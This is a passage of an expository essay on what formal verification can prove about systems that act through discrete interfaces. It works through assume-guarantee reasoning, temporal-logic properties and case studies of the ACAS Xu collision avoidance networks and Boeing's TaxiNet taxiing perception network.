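# What can be verified when an AI system acts through a discrete interface

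## What a discrete interface is and what a proof about it says

A discrete interface is a finite or typed set of symbols through which all of a system's decisions must pass. The system may take in camera images, radar returns or free text, but the part that chooses what to do receives only symbols such as "door open" or "obstacle ahead", or a request to run a named function with typed arguments (a tool call, when a language model makes it). Engineers have put such interfaces into aircraft guidance, trains, cars and language-model agents, partly because formal verification works well on small sets of symbols and badly on large neural networks. Formal verification uses mathematical proof and exhaustive search to establish how a program behaves.

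Information in these systems runs in a loop. Perception turns raw input from the world into a symbol, a decision rule maps that symbol to an action, and the action changes the state of the world. *Assumption Generation for the Verification of Learning-Enabled Autonomous Systems* (Păsăreanu, Mangal and colleagues, 2023) describes an airplane that steers itself along a taxiway in this way. A camera takes a picture, a neural network estimates the airplane's position from it, a controller turns the estimate into a steering command, and the airplane's dynamics determine where it goes next.

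Cutting the loop at the symbol leaves two very different halves. One contains the decision rule and a model of what its actions do. People wrote both, and can often list every possible state of each. The other half contains the network and the camera. Păsăreanu and colleagues give several reasons why it is hard to prove anything about this half: networks can have billions of parameters, small changes in the surroundings can flip their output, and they have no formal specification. The missing specification is the most fundamental problem. Engineers train a network on labelled pictures because nobody can write down which arrangements of pixels show a closed door, and a proof of correctness would need that description. It would also need a mathematical model of the lens, the lighting and the dirt.

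Zheng, Ruchkin and colleagues (2026), in *Assuring Learning-Enabled Cyber-Physical Systems with Foundation Models*, review tools that verify neural networks directly and note that some can handle networks of the size used for control and perception. But such a tool establishes a property over a specified set of inputs, and someone still has to connect that property to the behavior of the whole system. Zheng and colleagues prefer to work at the level where the requirement can be stated. Rules about collisions, for example, are stated in terms of objects, distances and changes over time, not pixels.

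### A robot and a door

A robot stands in front of a door. A detector processes the camera image and outputs one of two symbols, open or closed. The decision rule is to move forward if the output is open and to stay put otherwise. The door itself is either open or closed, so there are four possible combinations of door state and output.

| The door is | The detector reports | The robot | Result |
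|---|---|---|---|
| open | open | moves | goes through |
| open | closed | stays | waits for nothing |
| closed | closed | stays | waits, as it should |
| closed | open | moves | hits the door |

The robot never moves when the detector reports closed. Two rows have that report, and the robot stays put in both. We can check this without knowing anything about the camera. It is a property of the symbols, a claim about reported states and chosen actions that is true whether or not the reports are correct.

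The last row, however, refutes the claim that the robot never hits a closed door. Ruling out that row without changing the rule requires a premise, an assumption that the proof needs but does not establish. Here the premise is that the detector never reports a closed door as open. With it, the remaining three rows contain no collisions. This second claim is a property of the world, meaning that it concerns what physically happens, and the proof establishes it only if the premise about perception is true.

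The premise is narrower than "the detector is accurate". The second and fourth rows both contain a perception error, a symbol that does not match the actual state, but only the fourth ends in a collision. A detector that is right 99 times in 100 may make all its mistakes in that row, while one that always outputs closed satisfies the premise despite being wrong about every open door. An overall accuracy figure is therefore of little use without knowing which errors the property can tolerate. It is also easy to prove the first claim and advertise the second, since they sound similar in a one-line summary.

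### The assume-guarantee rule

The reasoning about the door is an instance of a general method. *Towards Unified Probabilistic Verification and Validation of Vision-Based Autonomy* (2025) describes assume-guarantee reasoning as a standard way to verify complex systems piece by piece, and for vision-based machines the usual pieces are an observer and a controller. Păsăreanu and colleagues write the rule with triples. The triple ⟨A, M, P⟩ is true if every system that contains component M and satisfies assumption A also has property P. The simplest form of the rule is then:

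⟨A, M₁, P⟩ and ⟨true, M₂, A⟩ together imply ⟨true, M₁ ∥ M₂, P⟩

If the decision part M₁ guarantees P under assumption A, and the perception part M₂ satisfies A unconditionally, then the two running together guarantee P. For the robot, M₁ is the moving rule plus the model of robot and door, M₂ is the camera plus the detector, A is "never reports a closed door as open", and P is "never hits a closed door". Checking the first triple means reading three rows of a table, while checking the second means proving that the detector won't report "open" for any image the camera could take of a closed door.

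The first half is usually provable. Păsăreanu and colleagues call the second half "infeasible" for a deep network and its camera. They work on the first half in two passes. In the first pass, they assume perfect perception, so that every actual state produces the matching report. Any violation they find must then come from the controller or the dynamics, and engineers can fix it before analyzing the network. In the second pass, they determine which errors the network can make without violating the property by computing the weakest assumption, which is the least demanding A that still suffices.

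A itself must then be supported by something other than proof. One option is to check the detector's outputs while the machine runs, and another is to estimate from data how large its errors are. *Statistical-Symbolic Verification of Perception-Based Autonomous Systems using State-Dependent Conformal Prediction* (2025) takes the second approach for numerical outputs, such as a car's position in its lane. It treats each output as the true value plus an error, so the safety argument needs a bound on the error but no model of the camera. The bound comes from a sample, so it applies to new conditions only as far as they resemble the sampled ones.

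Published guarantees are often vague about this half. *What Does It Take to Get Guarantees?* (Li, Faghfoorian and Ruchkin, 2025) extracted 423 assumptions and 321 guarantees from 104 papers on computer-controlled machines. Safety was the most common guarantee. The papers often underspecified their assumptions about sensing and perception, and rarely stated those about neural components explicitly. Li and colleagues selected the papers partly for variety, so the counts don't give rates for the whole field, but the gap is where the door example would lead one to look.

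### Kinds of property

"Never hits a closed door" is a safety property, a claim that something bad never happens. *Defining Liveness* (Alpern and Schneider, 1985) formalizes this idea. If a run violates a safety property, the violation happens at an identifiable point, and nothing afterwards can undo it. A liveness property is a claim that something required eventually happens, such as "whenever the detector reports open, the robot eventually moves." No finite part of a run can refute this claim, because the robot might still move later. A monitor, a component that watches outputs at run time, can therefore catch a safety violation when it occurs but can never catch a pure liveness violation. Adding a deadline ("moves within ten seconds") turns the requirement into a safety property, which a monitor can check.

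Liveness matters because a system that does nothing satisfies every safety property, as the programming newsletter Computer Things points out. For example, a robot that never moves will not hit a door.

Engineers write such requirements in temporal logic, a formal language for claims about order in time. Three operators are enough here. "Always p" means that p holds at every moment from now on, "eventually p" that it holds at some moment, and "p until q" that q happens at some moment and p holds at every moment before it. In this notation the two requirements on the robot become:

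- always (reported closed → not move)
- always (reported open → eventually move)

The formula "not move until reported open" forbids an early start, but it also requires that the detector eventually report open, which the robot's designers cannot guarantee. Alpern and Schneider use "until" as their example of a property that is neither pure safety nor pure liveness and splits into one part of each. Properties that restrict the order of events often need only the safety part. *Hyperproperties* (Clarkson and Schneider, 2009) gives the example that a system may not write to the network after it has read from a file.

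Information-flow properties are harder to handle because a single run cannot show that they hold. To check that a lobby screen shows the same thing whatever is in the confidential personnel file, one has to compare the run that took place with another in which the file was different. Clarkson and Schneider call such requirements hyperproperties and show that narrowing a program's possible behaviors can break them, although it can never break a safety or ordering property of single runs. For example, a program that may output 0, 1 or the value of a secret bit, with nothing fixing which, has the same possible outputs whatever the secret is. It therefore satisfies the policy that possible outputs do not depend on secrets. If the program is narrowed so that it always outputs the secret bit, it violates the policy, even though all of its remaining behaviors were possible before.

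Finally, a property may be probabilistic. *Probabilistic Model Checking* (Kwiatkowska, Norman and Parker, 2025) gives the example that a server takes more than one second to respond with probability at most 0.02. When a system's perception is imperfect, this is often the only kind of claim about the world that can be justified, because guaranteeing that an event never happens would require a detector that never makes an error that lets it happen.

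### Searching all the states

The four-row table was a search by hand. Model checking automates this search. Given a finite model and a temporal-logic formula, it searches all the model's states for a violation. If there is one, the output normally includes a counterexample, which is a step-by-step run that leads to the failure. For the robot, that run would be short (door closed, detector reports open, robot moves, collision). In their Turing Award lecture, *Model Checking*, the method's inventors Clarke, Emerson and Sifakis (2009) say that some people use it for the counterexamples alone.

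The main obstacle to model checking is the number of states. Clarke and colleagues estimate that plain enumeration can handle around a million. Compact representations can handle far more, but the number of states grows exponentially with the number of components. An n-bit counter, for example, has 2ⁿ states. A black-and-white picture of 100 by 100 pixels can take 2¹⁰⁰⁰⁰ values, whereas the door detector's output can take only two. This difference is the main reason to use a discrete interface.

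To check probabilistic properties, the model needs probabilities on its transitions. In a Markov chain, each state has a fixed probability of leading to each possible next state. In a Markov decision process, each state offers one or more actions, and each action has its own probabilities. *Probabilistic Model Checking Taken by Storm* (Volk, Heck and colleagues, 2026) explains the difference with a children's board game in which players try to pick all the fruit in an orchard before a raven arrives. The die roll is random, and the player has a real choice only when the die shows a basket, which allows any fruit to be picked. Fixing a strategy for those choices turns the decision process into a Markov chain. If the strategy is left open, a model checker can compute the best or worst probability over all strategies, in this case for a game with about 22,500 states. In a safety analysis, the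 open choices can stand for events to which nobody wants to assign probabilities, such as when a passer-by shuts the door.

Numbers from such a model deserve the same suspicion as any other claim about the world. Suppose the door stays closed, the robot checks it once a second, and the detector wrongly reports it open in 1 percent of checks. If the errors are independent, the probability of a collision within 100 checks is 1 − 0.99¹⁰⁰, or about 63 percent. If the errors instead come from a glare that has a 1 percent chance of being present, and is either there for the whole period or absent, the probability is 1 percent, even though the error rate per check is the same. Both calculations are exact, but neither shows which model fits the corridor.

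### Three premises

Any guarantee about the world that is derived from symbols rests on three premises. One is that the symbols are right, at least in the respects the property depends on. Checking a message's format cannot establish this, because "open" is a legal symbol whether or not the door is open. Zheng and colleagues warn that an error in converting sensor data into symbols can satisfy an interface's syntax and still invalidate the reasoning that follows. They want interfaces to include how uncertain each label is and how long it is valid, and to report an explicit "unknown" when the detector cannot classify its input reliably.

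Adding a third symbol, "unknown", means choosing between two rules that give the same action in all four rows of the table. "Move only if the report is open" keeps the robot still when the report is "unknown" or fails to arrive, while "stay only if the report is closed" sends it forward. *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (Saltzer and Schroeder, 1975), a founding text of computer security, recommends the first pattern, which it calls fail-safe defaults, where the system refuses unless there is a positive reason to permit. The paper argues that a mistake in the first kind of rule tends to block something that should be allowed, which people notice quickly, whereas a mistake in the second kind lets something through and may go unnoticed for years.

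Another premise is that the model of consequences is right. The table assumes that a robot that stays put cannot collide, though it could slide on a wet floor, and that an open door stays open while the robot passes, though a draft could close it. Li and colleagues distinguish an abstract guarantee, which is about a model, from an operational guarantee, which is about a deployed machine in its surroundings, and connect the two through assumptions. If the assumptions fail, the proof is still valid but supports no conclusion about the machine. Shields, which are components that remove actions judged unsafe in the reported state, depend on this premise as much as any other method, because they use the model to judge what is unsafe.

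The remaining premise is complete mediation, the condition that every consequential action passes through the check. Saltzer and Schroeder state it for computer files: "Every access to every object must be checked for authority." They apply it to initialization, recovery, shutdown and maintenance as well as normal operation, and advise skepticism about schemes that save time by remembering the result of an earlier check. A start-up routine that rolls the robot's wheels to calibrate them, a technician's joystick, or a ten-second-old report of "open" can each move the robot toward a closed door without the rule being applied to a current report. The first two would falsify even the property of the symbols, which requires no premise about perception but does require that only the rule drive the motors.

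Mediation is hard to establish because one must show that no path bypasses the check. This is easiest when the check is physically in the path. Saltzer and Schroeder describe hardware between a processor and its memory that compares every address with the limits set for the running program, so that no instruction can reach memory by another route. But some program must set those limits, so the machine needs a second check on which programs may change them, and a third to protect the bit that identifies the program requesting the change.

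## ACAS Xu: collision advisories checked with perfect sensors assumed

ACAS Xu is a collision avoidance system for unmanned aircraft. It belongs to ACAS X, a family of systems that the US Federal Aviation Administration began to support around 2010 as the successor to TCAS, which large airliners must carry today. These systems track nearby aircraft and recommend a maneuver in the last minute before a possible collision. For airliners, the maneuver is a climb or descent. Unmanned aircraft often climb less well, so ACAS Xu also recommends turns, as Katz, Moss and colleagues (2025) explain in *Aircraft Collision Avoidance Systems*.

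Researchers who verify neural networks have used the turn logic as a test case since 2017. They usually assume that its inputs are exact, as Păsăreanu and colleagues do in the first pass of their method.

### Seven values in, one advisory out

The aircraft that carries the system is the ownship, and the aircraft it must avoid is the intruder. The turn logic receives seven values:

| Symbol | Meaning |
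|---|---|
| ρ | distance to the intruder, in feet |
| θ | direction to the intruder, measured from the ownship's heading |
| ψ | the intruder's heading relative to the ownship's |
| v_own | the ownship's speed, in feet per second |
| v_int | the intruder's speed, in feet per second |
| τ | seconds until the two aircraft lose their vertical separation |
| a_prev | the previous advisory |

The output is one of five advisories: clear of conflict (COC), weak left, weak right, strong left or strong right. A weak turn changes the heading by 1.5 degrees per second and a strong turn by 3. The interface is discrete on the output side, but most of the inputs can take any value in a range, so the number of possible situations is still infinite.

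The designers computed the decision rule rather than writing it by hand. They modeled an encounter as a Markov decision process in which the intruder accelerates at random and the pilot responds after a random delay. A collision carries a large penalty, and issuing, strengthening or reversing an advisory carries a smaller one. They divided the states into a grid and worked backwards from the moment of collision to compute the expected future penalty of each advisory in each state. The system looks up these values in a table and picks the advisory with the lowest one. Because this minimizes an average penalty that includes nuisance alerts, it doesn't guarantee that every encounter ends without a collision.

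*Compressing ACAS-Xu Lookup Tables with Binary Decision Diagrams* (Boniol, Brunel and colleagues, 2026) describes a table with 89,799,840 states for each of the five previous advisories. Its grid has 10 values of τ, 41 distances, 39 values for each angle and 12 for each speed. To fit the logic into existing avionics, Julian, Kochenderfer and Owen (2018), in *Deep Neural Network Compression for Aircraft Collision Avoidance Systems*, trained neural networks to approximate the table, cutting storage by a factor of 1,000.

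The version that became the test case has 45 small networks, one for each combination of the five previous advisories and nine values of τ. Each network reads the other five inputs and scores each advisory, and the system selects the advisory with the lowest score. *Reluplex* (Katz, Barrett and colleagues, 2017) reports that the table takes up over 2 GB and the networks under 3 MB.

### What the network proofs established

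Reluplex is an algorithm that proves properties of such networks. Each of the 300 hidden units in an ACAS Xu network computes a weighted sum x of its inputs and outputs max(0, x), so it either passes the sum on or outputs zero. If we knew which of the two each unit does, the network would be a linear function and standard linear programming could analyze it, but there are up to 2³⁰⁰ combinations. Reluplex extends the simplex method, an algorithm for linear programming, to leave most of these choices open and split into cases only when it must. It searches for an input that violates the property. If it shows that none exists, the property holds for every input in the region.

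Katz, Barrett and colleagues checked ten properties. The third, φ₃, concerns an intruder that is directly ahead and flying toward the ownship, and requires that the network not output "clear of conflict". In symbols, with angles in radians:

1500 ≤ ρ ≤ 1800, −0.06 ≤ θ ≤ 0.06, ψ ≥ 3.10, v_own ≥ 980, v_int ≥ 960
⟹ score(COC) > min{score(weak left), score(weak right), score(strong left), score(strong right)}

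Reluplex proved φ₃ for all 42 networks tested, in just under eight hours of computing. It timed out on another property. A different property requires the network to output either "weak left" or "clear of conflict" when vertical separation is large and the previous advisory was "weak left". For this property, Reluplex found an input for which the network's output differed from the table's, and the designers planned to retrain the network.

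The tools have since become much faster. *The 7th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2026)* (2026) still uses the ten original properties, in 186 combinations of property and network, and allows 116 seconds for each. The original runs took from seconds to days, and some never finished.

Faster verification doesn't change what the properties mean, however. φ₃ relates one set of reported numbers to one advisory and doesn't specify which way to turn. It implies little about collisions. At the speeds in φ₃, the aircraft approach each other at 1,940 feet per second or more, so from 1,800 feet apart they meet in less than a second. If they are at the same altitude, a turn of 3 degrees per second comes far too late to prevent a collision, even though the network satisfies φ₃.

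A proof about the networks also does not apply to the table they approximate. Boniol and colleagues compared five of the networks with the table and found that they agreed in 92 to 99 percent of the states where the table gives "clear of conflict", but in only 57 to 70 percent of the states where it calls for a turn. An average over all states would hide the lower agreement on turns, because the table gives "clear of conflict" in most states.

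They also compressed the table without loss into decision diagrams (graphs that merge identical parts of a decision tree), which took under 3 MB for each previous advisory, and checked the ten properties on those. Some of the properties failed on the table itself. For example, one property requires "strong right" when an intruder is near and approaching from the left. It holds if the previous advisory was "clear of conflict", the only case that Katz, Barrett and colleagues tested, but not if it was "weak right" or "strong right". Boniol and colleagues ask whether the table or the properties should count as the correct description of the system, and I don't think we can tell from the proofs.

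Another recent approach keeps a network and stores its mistakes separately. Christensen, Stefani and colleagues (2026), in *On the Applicability of Safety Nets*, ran networks for simplified versions of ACAS X on every point of the grid and put each wrong answer into a small lookup table, which the system checks before using the network. The combination matches the original at every grid point, though not necessarily between them. This match doesn't show that aircraft following the advisories will stay apart.

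### Searching backwards from collisions

To answer that question one has to close the loop: the advisory turns the aircraft, the turn changes the inputs, and a second later the networks produce another advisory. Bak and Tran (2022), in *Neural Network Compression of ACAS Xu Early Prototype is Unsafe*, did this for the 45 networks. They made the conditions as favorable as they could:

- The intruder flies straight at constant speed.
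- The ownship also keeps a constant speed, and its rate of turn changes only once a second.
- The ownship follows each advisory immediately and exactly, and flies straight on when the output is "clear of conflict".
- The sensors make no errors.

These assumptions make a safety proof less useful, since real encounters violate them, but they make a counterexample more convincing, because neither the pilot nor the sensors can be at fault if the aircraft collide. A collision here means a near mid-air collision, in which the aircraft come within 500 feet horizontally with no vertical separation left. Each encounter starts with the aircraft more than 60,760 feet apart, outside the range in which the system is active.

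Bak and Tran first make the set of possible inputs finite by modifying the system to round the state to a grid before it runs a network. All states in a grid cell then lead to the same advisory, so running the network once per cell is enough to find it. The method doesn't require reasoning about the network's individual units, so it works for any type of network. But it is practical only for networks with few inputs, because the number of cells grows exponentially with the number of inputs.

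The next step is to cover all possible collisions with cells. The coarsest grid has steps of 500 feet in position, 100 feet per second in speed and 1.5 degrees in heading. This takes 4 cells for position, 11 for the ownship's speed, 12 for the intruder's speed and 240 for heading. With five previous advisories and two cases for vertical motion, the search has 1,267,200 starting points.

The algorithm works backwards in time from each collision cell. Suppose the last advisory before the collision was "weak right". The equations of motion are linear within each second, so the algorithm can compute exactly which states, one second earlier, lead into the collision cell through a weak right turn. It then runs the networks on the grid cells that cover those states and keeps only the cells where the output is "weak right". It repeats this process from the remaining cells, going back one second each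 time. If no cells remain, that collision cannot happen. If the search reaches a state in which the aircraft are more than 60,760 feet apart, it has found a complete path from ordinary flight to a collision.

Such a path might exist only because of the rounding. Bak and Tran therefore take a starting state from it and replay the encounter on the original networks without rounding. If the aircraft still collide, the counterexample is genuine. If they don't, the algorithm halves one of the grid steps and searches again. Bak and Tran prove that this procedure eventually either shows that the rounded system is safe or finds a collision in the original one. A safety proof covers only the rounded system, so it would apply to an aircraft only if the aircraft's software did the same rounding.

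### The collisions they found

The search usually took less than a minute to find a collision that also occurred without rounding. In one, the ownship flies at 140 feet per second and the intruder at 1,113. The networks output a turn as soon as the intruder comes into range, but the ownship is too slow to get away. A longer range might have prevented the collision.

In another case, which is harder to excuse, a fast intruder approaches from behind while the ownship is already moving away from its path. After several seconds of "clear of conflict", the networks output "weak right" and keep doing so for most of the next minute. Without the system there would have been no collision, but the turn brings the ownship back into the intruder's path, and the two aircraft come within 254 feet of each other.

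None of the ten Reluplex properties applies at any moment of that encounter. Four require an ownship speed of at least 980 feet per second, and this ownship flies at 114. The other six concern networks or relative headings that don't occur in the encounter. The advisories that led to the collision are therefore consistent with everything Katz, Barrett and colleagues proved. Adding more properties like φ₃ would not be enough, because whether a turn is safe depends on the advisories that follow it. If a rule only requires some turn whenever an intruder is ahead, a network can satisfy it by alternating between left and right, which keeps the aircraft flying almost straight.

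A third collision, with a slow intruder, took 159 seconds to develop. Shortly before the collision, the output switched from "weak left" to "strong right". At that moment the intruder was directly behind the ownship, where the angle θ jumps from −π to π even though the aircraft have barely moved. Bak and Tran consider the jump in θ the likely cause.

They proved the rounded system safe for part of the operating range, ownship speeds between 1,000 and 1,200 feet per second, using a finer grid. The proof took about 32 minutes and covered 3.7 million cases. Just below that range, at 964 feet per second, they found a collision in which the final distance was 498.5 feet, slightly under the 500-foot limit.

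Whether the system can be proved safe depends heavily on the speeds assumed. Julian and Kochenderfer (2019), in *Guaranteeing Safety for Neural Network-Based Aircraft Collision Avoidance Systems*, had earlier proved closed-loop safety for simpler networks, with the speeds fixed at 200 and 185 feet per second in the horizontal case. When Bak and Tran fixed the same two speeds, their method proved the rounded version of the larger networks safe in about a minute. A system can therefore be provably safe at one pair of speeds even though many collisions occur within the full range of speeds.

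Random testing finds some of these collisions but misses the more surprising ones. Bak and Tran simulated encounters in batches of 1.5 million, the number used in an earlier evaluation of the networks. With both aircraft at the same altitude, a batch averaged about 17 collisions. Across 100 such batches, no collision involved an ownship faster than 452 feet per second, whereas the backward search found one at 882 feet per second.

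All of this concerns an early prototype. Bak and Tran replayed the encounters with the networks but not with the table, so their results don't show whether the compression introduced these collisions or whether they would also have happened with the table.

### Proofs that start from the motion

Verification can also start from the physics and leave the network until later. In *A Formally Verified Hybrid System for Safe Advisories*, Jeannin, Ghorbal and colleagues (2016) modeled ACAS X as a hybrid system, which combines discrete decisions with continuous motion. They determined the relative positions and speeds at which an advisory is safe, and proved the result with a theorem prover. Their proofs also cover later advisories that change the first one. An earlier paper, *A Formally Verified Hybrid System for the Next-Generation Airborne Collision Avoidance System*, compared such safe regions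 with the advisories of the actual system at the time and found conflicts.

These proofs apply to flight, which φ₃ does not, but they depend on assumptions about how each aircraft is flown. In *Formally Verified Next-Generation Airborne Collision Avoidance Games in ACAS X*, Cleaveland, Mitsch and Platzer (2021) criticize existing analyses for severely restricting the intruder's maneuvers, and instead treat the encounter as a game.

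The two lines of work can be joined. Teuber, Mitsch and Platzer (2024), in *Provably Safe Neural Network Controllers via Differential Dynamic Logic*, start from a rule that lists the allowed actions in each state and that someone has already proved safe for unlimited time. From that proof they derive a test for the network g:

for every state x: Inv(x) ⟹ Allowed(x, g(x))

Inv is a set of safe states that the system never leaves as long as it takes allowed actions. Like φ₃, the test covers single decisions. But if the network passes, each decision keeps the system in Inv, where the test applies again, so the whole flight is safe. Allowed actions don't keep the aircraft inside the region in φ₃, and they leave it within a second. For networks that give vertical ACAS X advisories, Teuber and colleagues proved safety in some scenarios, and in others they listed all the regions where the network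 fails the test.

### Adding sensor error

The real ACAS X allows for sensor error. According to Katz, Moss and colleagues, its tracking software outputs a set of possible states with weights, and the system uses those weights to average the costs in the table. It picks the advisory a that minimizes Σ b(s)·C(s, a), where b(s) is the weight of state s and C(s, a) is the cost of advisory a in that state.

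A property that holds in every state can fail after this averaging. Suppose two states are equally likely and the system chooses the advisory with the lowest score. In one state, a left turn scores 1, a right turn 12 and "clear of conflict" 5. In the other, the scores for left and right are swapped. "Clear of conflict" is not the best choice in either state, so a property like φ₃ holds in both. But on average each turn scores 6.5 and "clear of conflict" still scores 5, so the system would choose it. That choice may be sensible, since waiting a moment could reveal which way to turn. Still, a proof about exact inputs doesn't establish what the system does with uncertain ones.

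One earlier evaluation simulated the networks with sensor noise and found a collision probability of about 1 in 10,000. But, as Bak and Tran point out, such a figure doesn't separate collisions caused by noise from those caused by the networks. They also note that Julian and Kochenderfer's method can allow for sensor uncertainty, pilot delay and inexact turns, though only on the simpler system. Julian and Kochenderfer found that looser limits on how the aircraft move can bring back potentially unsafe encounters.

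*Robust Verification of Controllers under State Uncertainty via Hamilton-Jacobi Reachability Analysis* (2025) presents a general method for closed-loop verification when the controller receives an inexact state. It does not prove that ACAS Xu is safe, and the bound on sensor error has to come from measurements like those for TaxiNet, where a network steers an aircraft using camera images.

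## TaxiNet: an aircraft steered by a network that reads camera images

The self-steering airplane given above as the first example of a perception loop is an experimental Boeing system. Its neural network, TaxiNet, helps it follow the taxiway's center line. Bak and Tran could cover the five inputs of an ACAS Xu network with a grid, but no grid could cover the 216,000 numbers in a TaxiNet picture, which has 360 by 200 pixels in three colors. Verification therefore has to start from the network's outputs.

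For each picture, TaxiNet outputs estimates of the cross-track error (the airplane's distance from the center line in meters) and the heading error (the angle between the airplane's heading and the center line). In *Closed-loop Analysis of Vision-based Autonomous Systems*, Păsăreanu, Mangal and colleagues (2023) evaluated the network on 11,108 pictures from Boeing. On average, its position estimates were wrong by 1.2 meters and its heading estimates by 7.9 degrees. Boeing also required that the airplane stay within 8 meters of the center line, so that it doesn't leave the taxiway, and that its heading stay within 35 degrees of the center line, because a larger error would make it hard to maneuver back.

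### Fifteen states and three commands

Păsăreanu and colleagues made the system finite by dividing the taxiway into five strips and the heading into three ranges. *Scenario-based Compositional Verification of Autonomous Systems with Neural Perception* (Watson, Alur and colleagues, 2025) reuses this model and lists its boundaries. The center strip extends 1.6 meters to each side of the center line, the left and right strips run from there to 4.8 meters, and the far left and far right strips end at the 8-meter limit. A heading counts as straight if it is within about 11.7 degrees of the center line. The five strips and three heading ranges give 15 states, plus an error state for each broken limit. The network's outputs always lie inside the limits, so they can never indicate that the airplane has left the taxiway.

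The controller has three commands and chooses between them as follows:

| Reported position | Reported heading left | Reported heading straight | Reported heading right |
|---|---|---|---|
| left or far left | turn right | turn right | go straight |
| center | turn right | go straight | turn left |
| right or far right | go straight | turn left | turn left |

The model of the airplane's motion is equally coarse. If the airplane is heading straight, a right turn points it to the right and moves it one strip to the right. If it is heading right, "go straight" moves it another strip to the right, a left turn straightens it without moving it sideways, and another right turn exceeds the heading limit. Any move outward from a far strip takes it off the taxiway. Left turns are the mirror image of right turns.

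This controller is safe when every report is correct. Following its rules from each of the 15 states shows that the airplane returns to the center strip, heading straight, in at most four moves without breaking a limit. From a perfectly centered start, the airplane goes straight forever, so any failure from that start must come from perception errors.

### Replacing the camera with a table of counts

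Păsăreanu and colleagues replace the camera and the network with a random choice of report. The probabilities come from a confusion matrix, a table that counts how often each actual state gets each possible report. This is the matrix for heading:

| Actual heading | Reported straight | Reported left | Reported right | Pictures |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| straight | 4,748 | 2,139 | 148 | 7,035 |
| left | 91 | 2,010 | 0 | 2,101 |
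| right | 744 | 211 | 1,017 | 1,972 |

If C(s, r) is the number of pictures taken in state s for which the network reported r, the estimated probability of that report is:

α(s, r) = C(s, r) / Σ C(s, r′), summed over all reports r′

An airplane that is heading straight thus gets the report "straight" with probability 4,748 / 7,035, or 0.675, and the report "left" with probability 0.304. Overall, 70 percent of the heading reports and 62 percent of the position reports are correct, but accuracy varies widely with the airplane's actual heading and position. The network reports a left heading correctly in 96 percent of cases and a right heading in only 52 percent, perhaps because of where the camera sits. It reports the center strip correctly 84 percent of the time but the far-left strip only 25 percent of the time, and it reports 38 percent of the far-left pictures as center. Păsăreanu and colleagues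 attribute the good results at the center to training runs that mostly followed the line. As a result, the reports are least reliable near the edge of the taxiway, where an error is most dangerous.

Combining these probabilities with the controller and the motion model gives a Markov chain, which the probabilistic model checker PRISM can analyze. For the first limit, the query P=? [F (cte = −1)] gives the probability that the airplane ever leaves the taxiway, where F means "eventually" and −1 marks the error state. The size of the chain depends on the number of possible reports, not the size of the network, so the method would work just as well for a network with a billion parameters.

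The published model simplifies by assuming that the position and heading errors in one picture are independent of each other, and that each picture's errors are independent of the previous picture's. Păsăreanu and colleagues note that a joint matrix for position and heading would remove the first assumption. The second is the assumption that changed the robot's collision probability from 1 percent to 63 percent in the glare example.

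### Two moves by hand

Suppose the airplane starts in the center strip and is heading straight. The position report is "center" with probability 0.842, "right" with probability 0.148 and "left" with probability 0.010. The heading report is "straight", "left" or "right" with probabilities 0.675, 0.304 and 0.021. The controller orders a right turn if the report is "center" and "left", or if the position report is "left" and the heading report is anything but "right". Adding these cases, and doing the same for left turns, gives:

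P(turn right) = 0.842 × 0.304 + 0.010 × (0.675 + 0.304) ≈ 0.266
P(turn left) = 0.842 × 0.021 + 0.148 × (0.675 + 0.021) ≈ 0.121

So even when the airplane is centered and pointed straight, the controller makes a needless turn 39 percent of the time. It goes straight the other 61 percent of the time, sometimes only because two errors cancel. For example, if the network outputs "right of center" and "heading left", both are wrong, but together they produce the correct command.

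After a needless right turn the airplane is in the right strip and heading right, and it needs to turn left. The network is poor at recognizing this heading. The controller orders the left turn with probability 0.764, goes straight with probability 0.199 and turns right again with probability 0.037. That second right turn breaks the heading limit:

P(second right turn) = 0.339 × 0.107 + 0.001 × (0.377 + 0.107) ≈ 0.037
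P(heading limit broken by the second move) ≈ 0.266 × 0.037 ≈ 0.0098

A needless left turn adds only about 0.000005 to this probability, because the network classified none of the 2,101 pictures taken with the aircraft heading left as heading right. The total is just under 1 percent after two moves.

Leaving the taxiway takes at least three moves. After the needless right turn, the controller has to go straight twice, taking the airplane through the far right strip and over the edge. The probability of this sequence is 0.266 × 0.199 × 0.172, or about 0.9 percent. PRISM does the same arithmetic for longer runs, and takes less than a tenth of a second for 30 steps. These figures describe a very simplified airplane that moves sideways a whole strip at a time, and Watson and colleagues advise treating error probabilities from such models with caution. The comparison with perfect reports is more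 informative than the exact values.

### A guard on the network and intervals on the probabilities

Păsăreanu and colleagues then added a run-time guard that rejects pictures on which the network is likely to be wrong. To build it, they ran the network on a separate set of 5,554 pictures and recorded the values of its internal neurons. They then used decision trees to find combinations of values that went with errors above 1 meter or 5 degrees. One of the resulting rules matched 755 pictures, and the network had made such an error on all of them. When a new picture matches a rule, the system discards it and takes another, and after ten rejections in a row it aborts. In the 2023 slides *Compositional Verification and Runtime Monitoring for Learning-Enabled Autonomous Systems*, Păsăreanu suggests handing control to the pilot at that point.

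Of the 11,108 pictures, 9,125 (82.1 percent) passed the guard. On those, heading accuracy rose from 70 to 76 percent and position accuracy from 62 to 66 percent. These gains are modest, but they have a larger effect on safety. Repeating the calculation above with the new matrix gives a probability of about 0.4 percent that the aircraft breaks the heading limit within two moves, less than half the earlier figure. The probability falls this much because the guard removes many of the pictures in which a right heading looks like a left one.

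In the model, the guard almost never aborts, because the probability of ten rejections in a row is 0.179¹⁰, or about 3 in 100 million. This figure holds only if successive pictures are independent. If the guard rejects a picture because of low sun on wet concrete, the next picture from the same spot will probably look much the same, so real aborts could be far more common.

The probabilities in the matrix are estimates from a finite sample, so Păsăreanu and colleagues replaced each one with an unknown parameter and gave the counts to FACT, a tool that computes a confidence interval for the probability that a limit is broken. Even with every zero-count transition left out, they could not get past a horizon of four steps (three moves in the published code) within two hours. Leaving out those transitions is not strictly justified, because a count of zero in 2,101 pictures is still compatible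 with a true probability of nearly 0.2 percent, but the difference was very small in the one case they could compute both ways.

A confidence interval of this kind accounts only for random variation in which pictures were sampled. It would be just as narrow if Boeing had taken all the pictures on one sunny afternoon, even though they wouldn't represent other weather or times of day.

### The weakest assumption on the reports

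In the group's other paper, *Assumption Generation*, Păsăreanu and colleagues don't use the camera images. They let the network report anything in any state and compute which sequences of reports keep the airplane safe. This gives the weakest assumption for the assume-guarantee rule. A perception system satisfies that assumption if and only if the airplane stays within its limits with the system installed.

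Their smallest model has three strips (left, center and right, with boundaries 2.7 meters from the line) and the same three headings, so there are nine possible reports. The controller is the one in the table above. They construct the assumption in these steps:

1. They combine the controller and the motion model, allow every report in every state, and add an error state for broken limits.
2. They propagate errors backwards. If a state leads to the error through steps that perception cannot influence, it also counts as an error.
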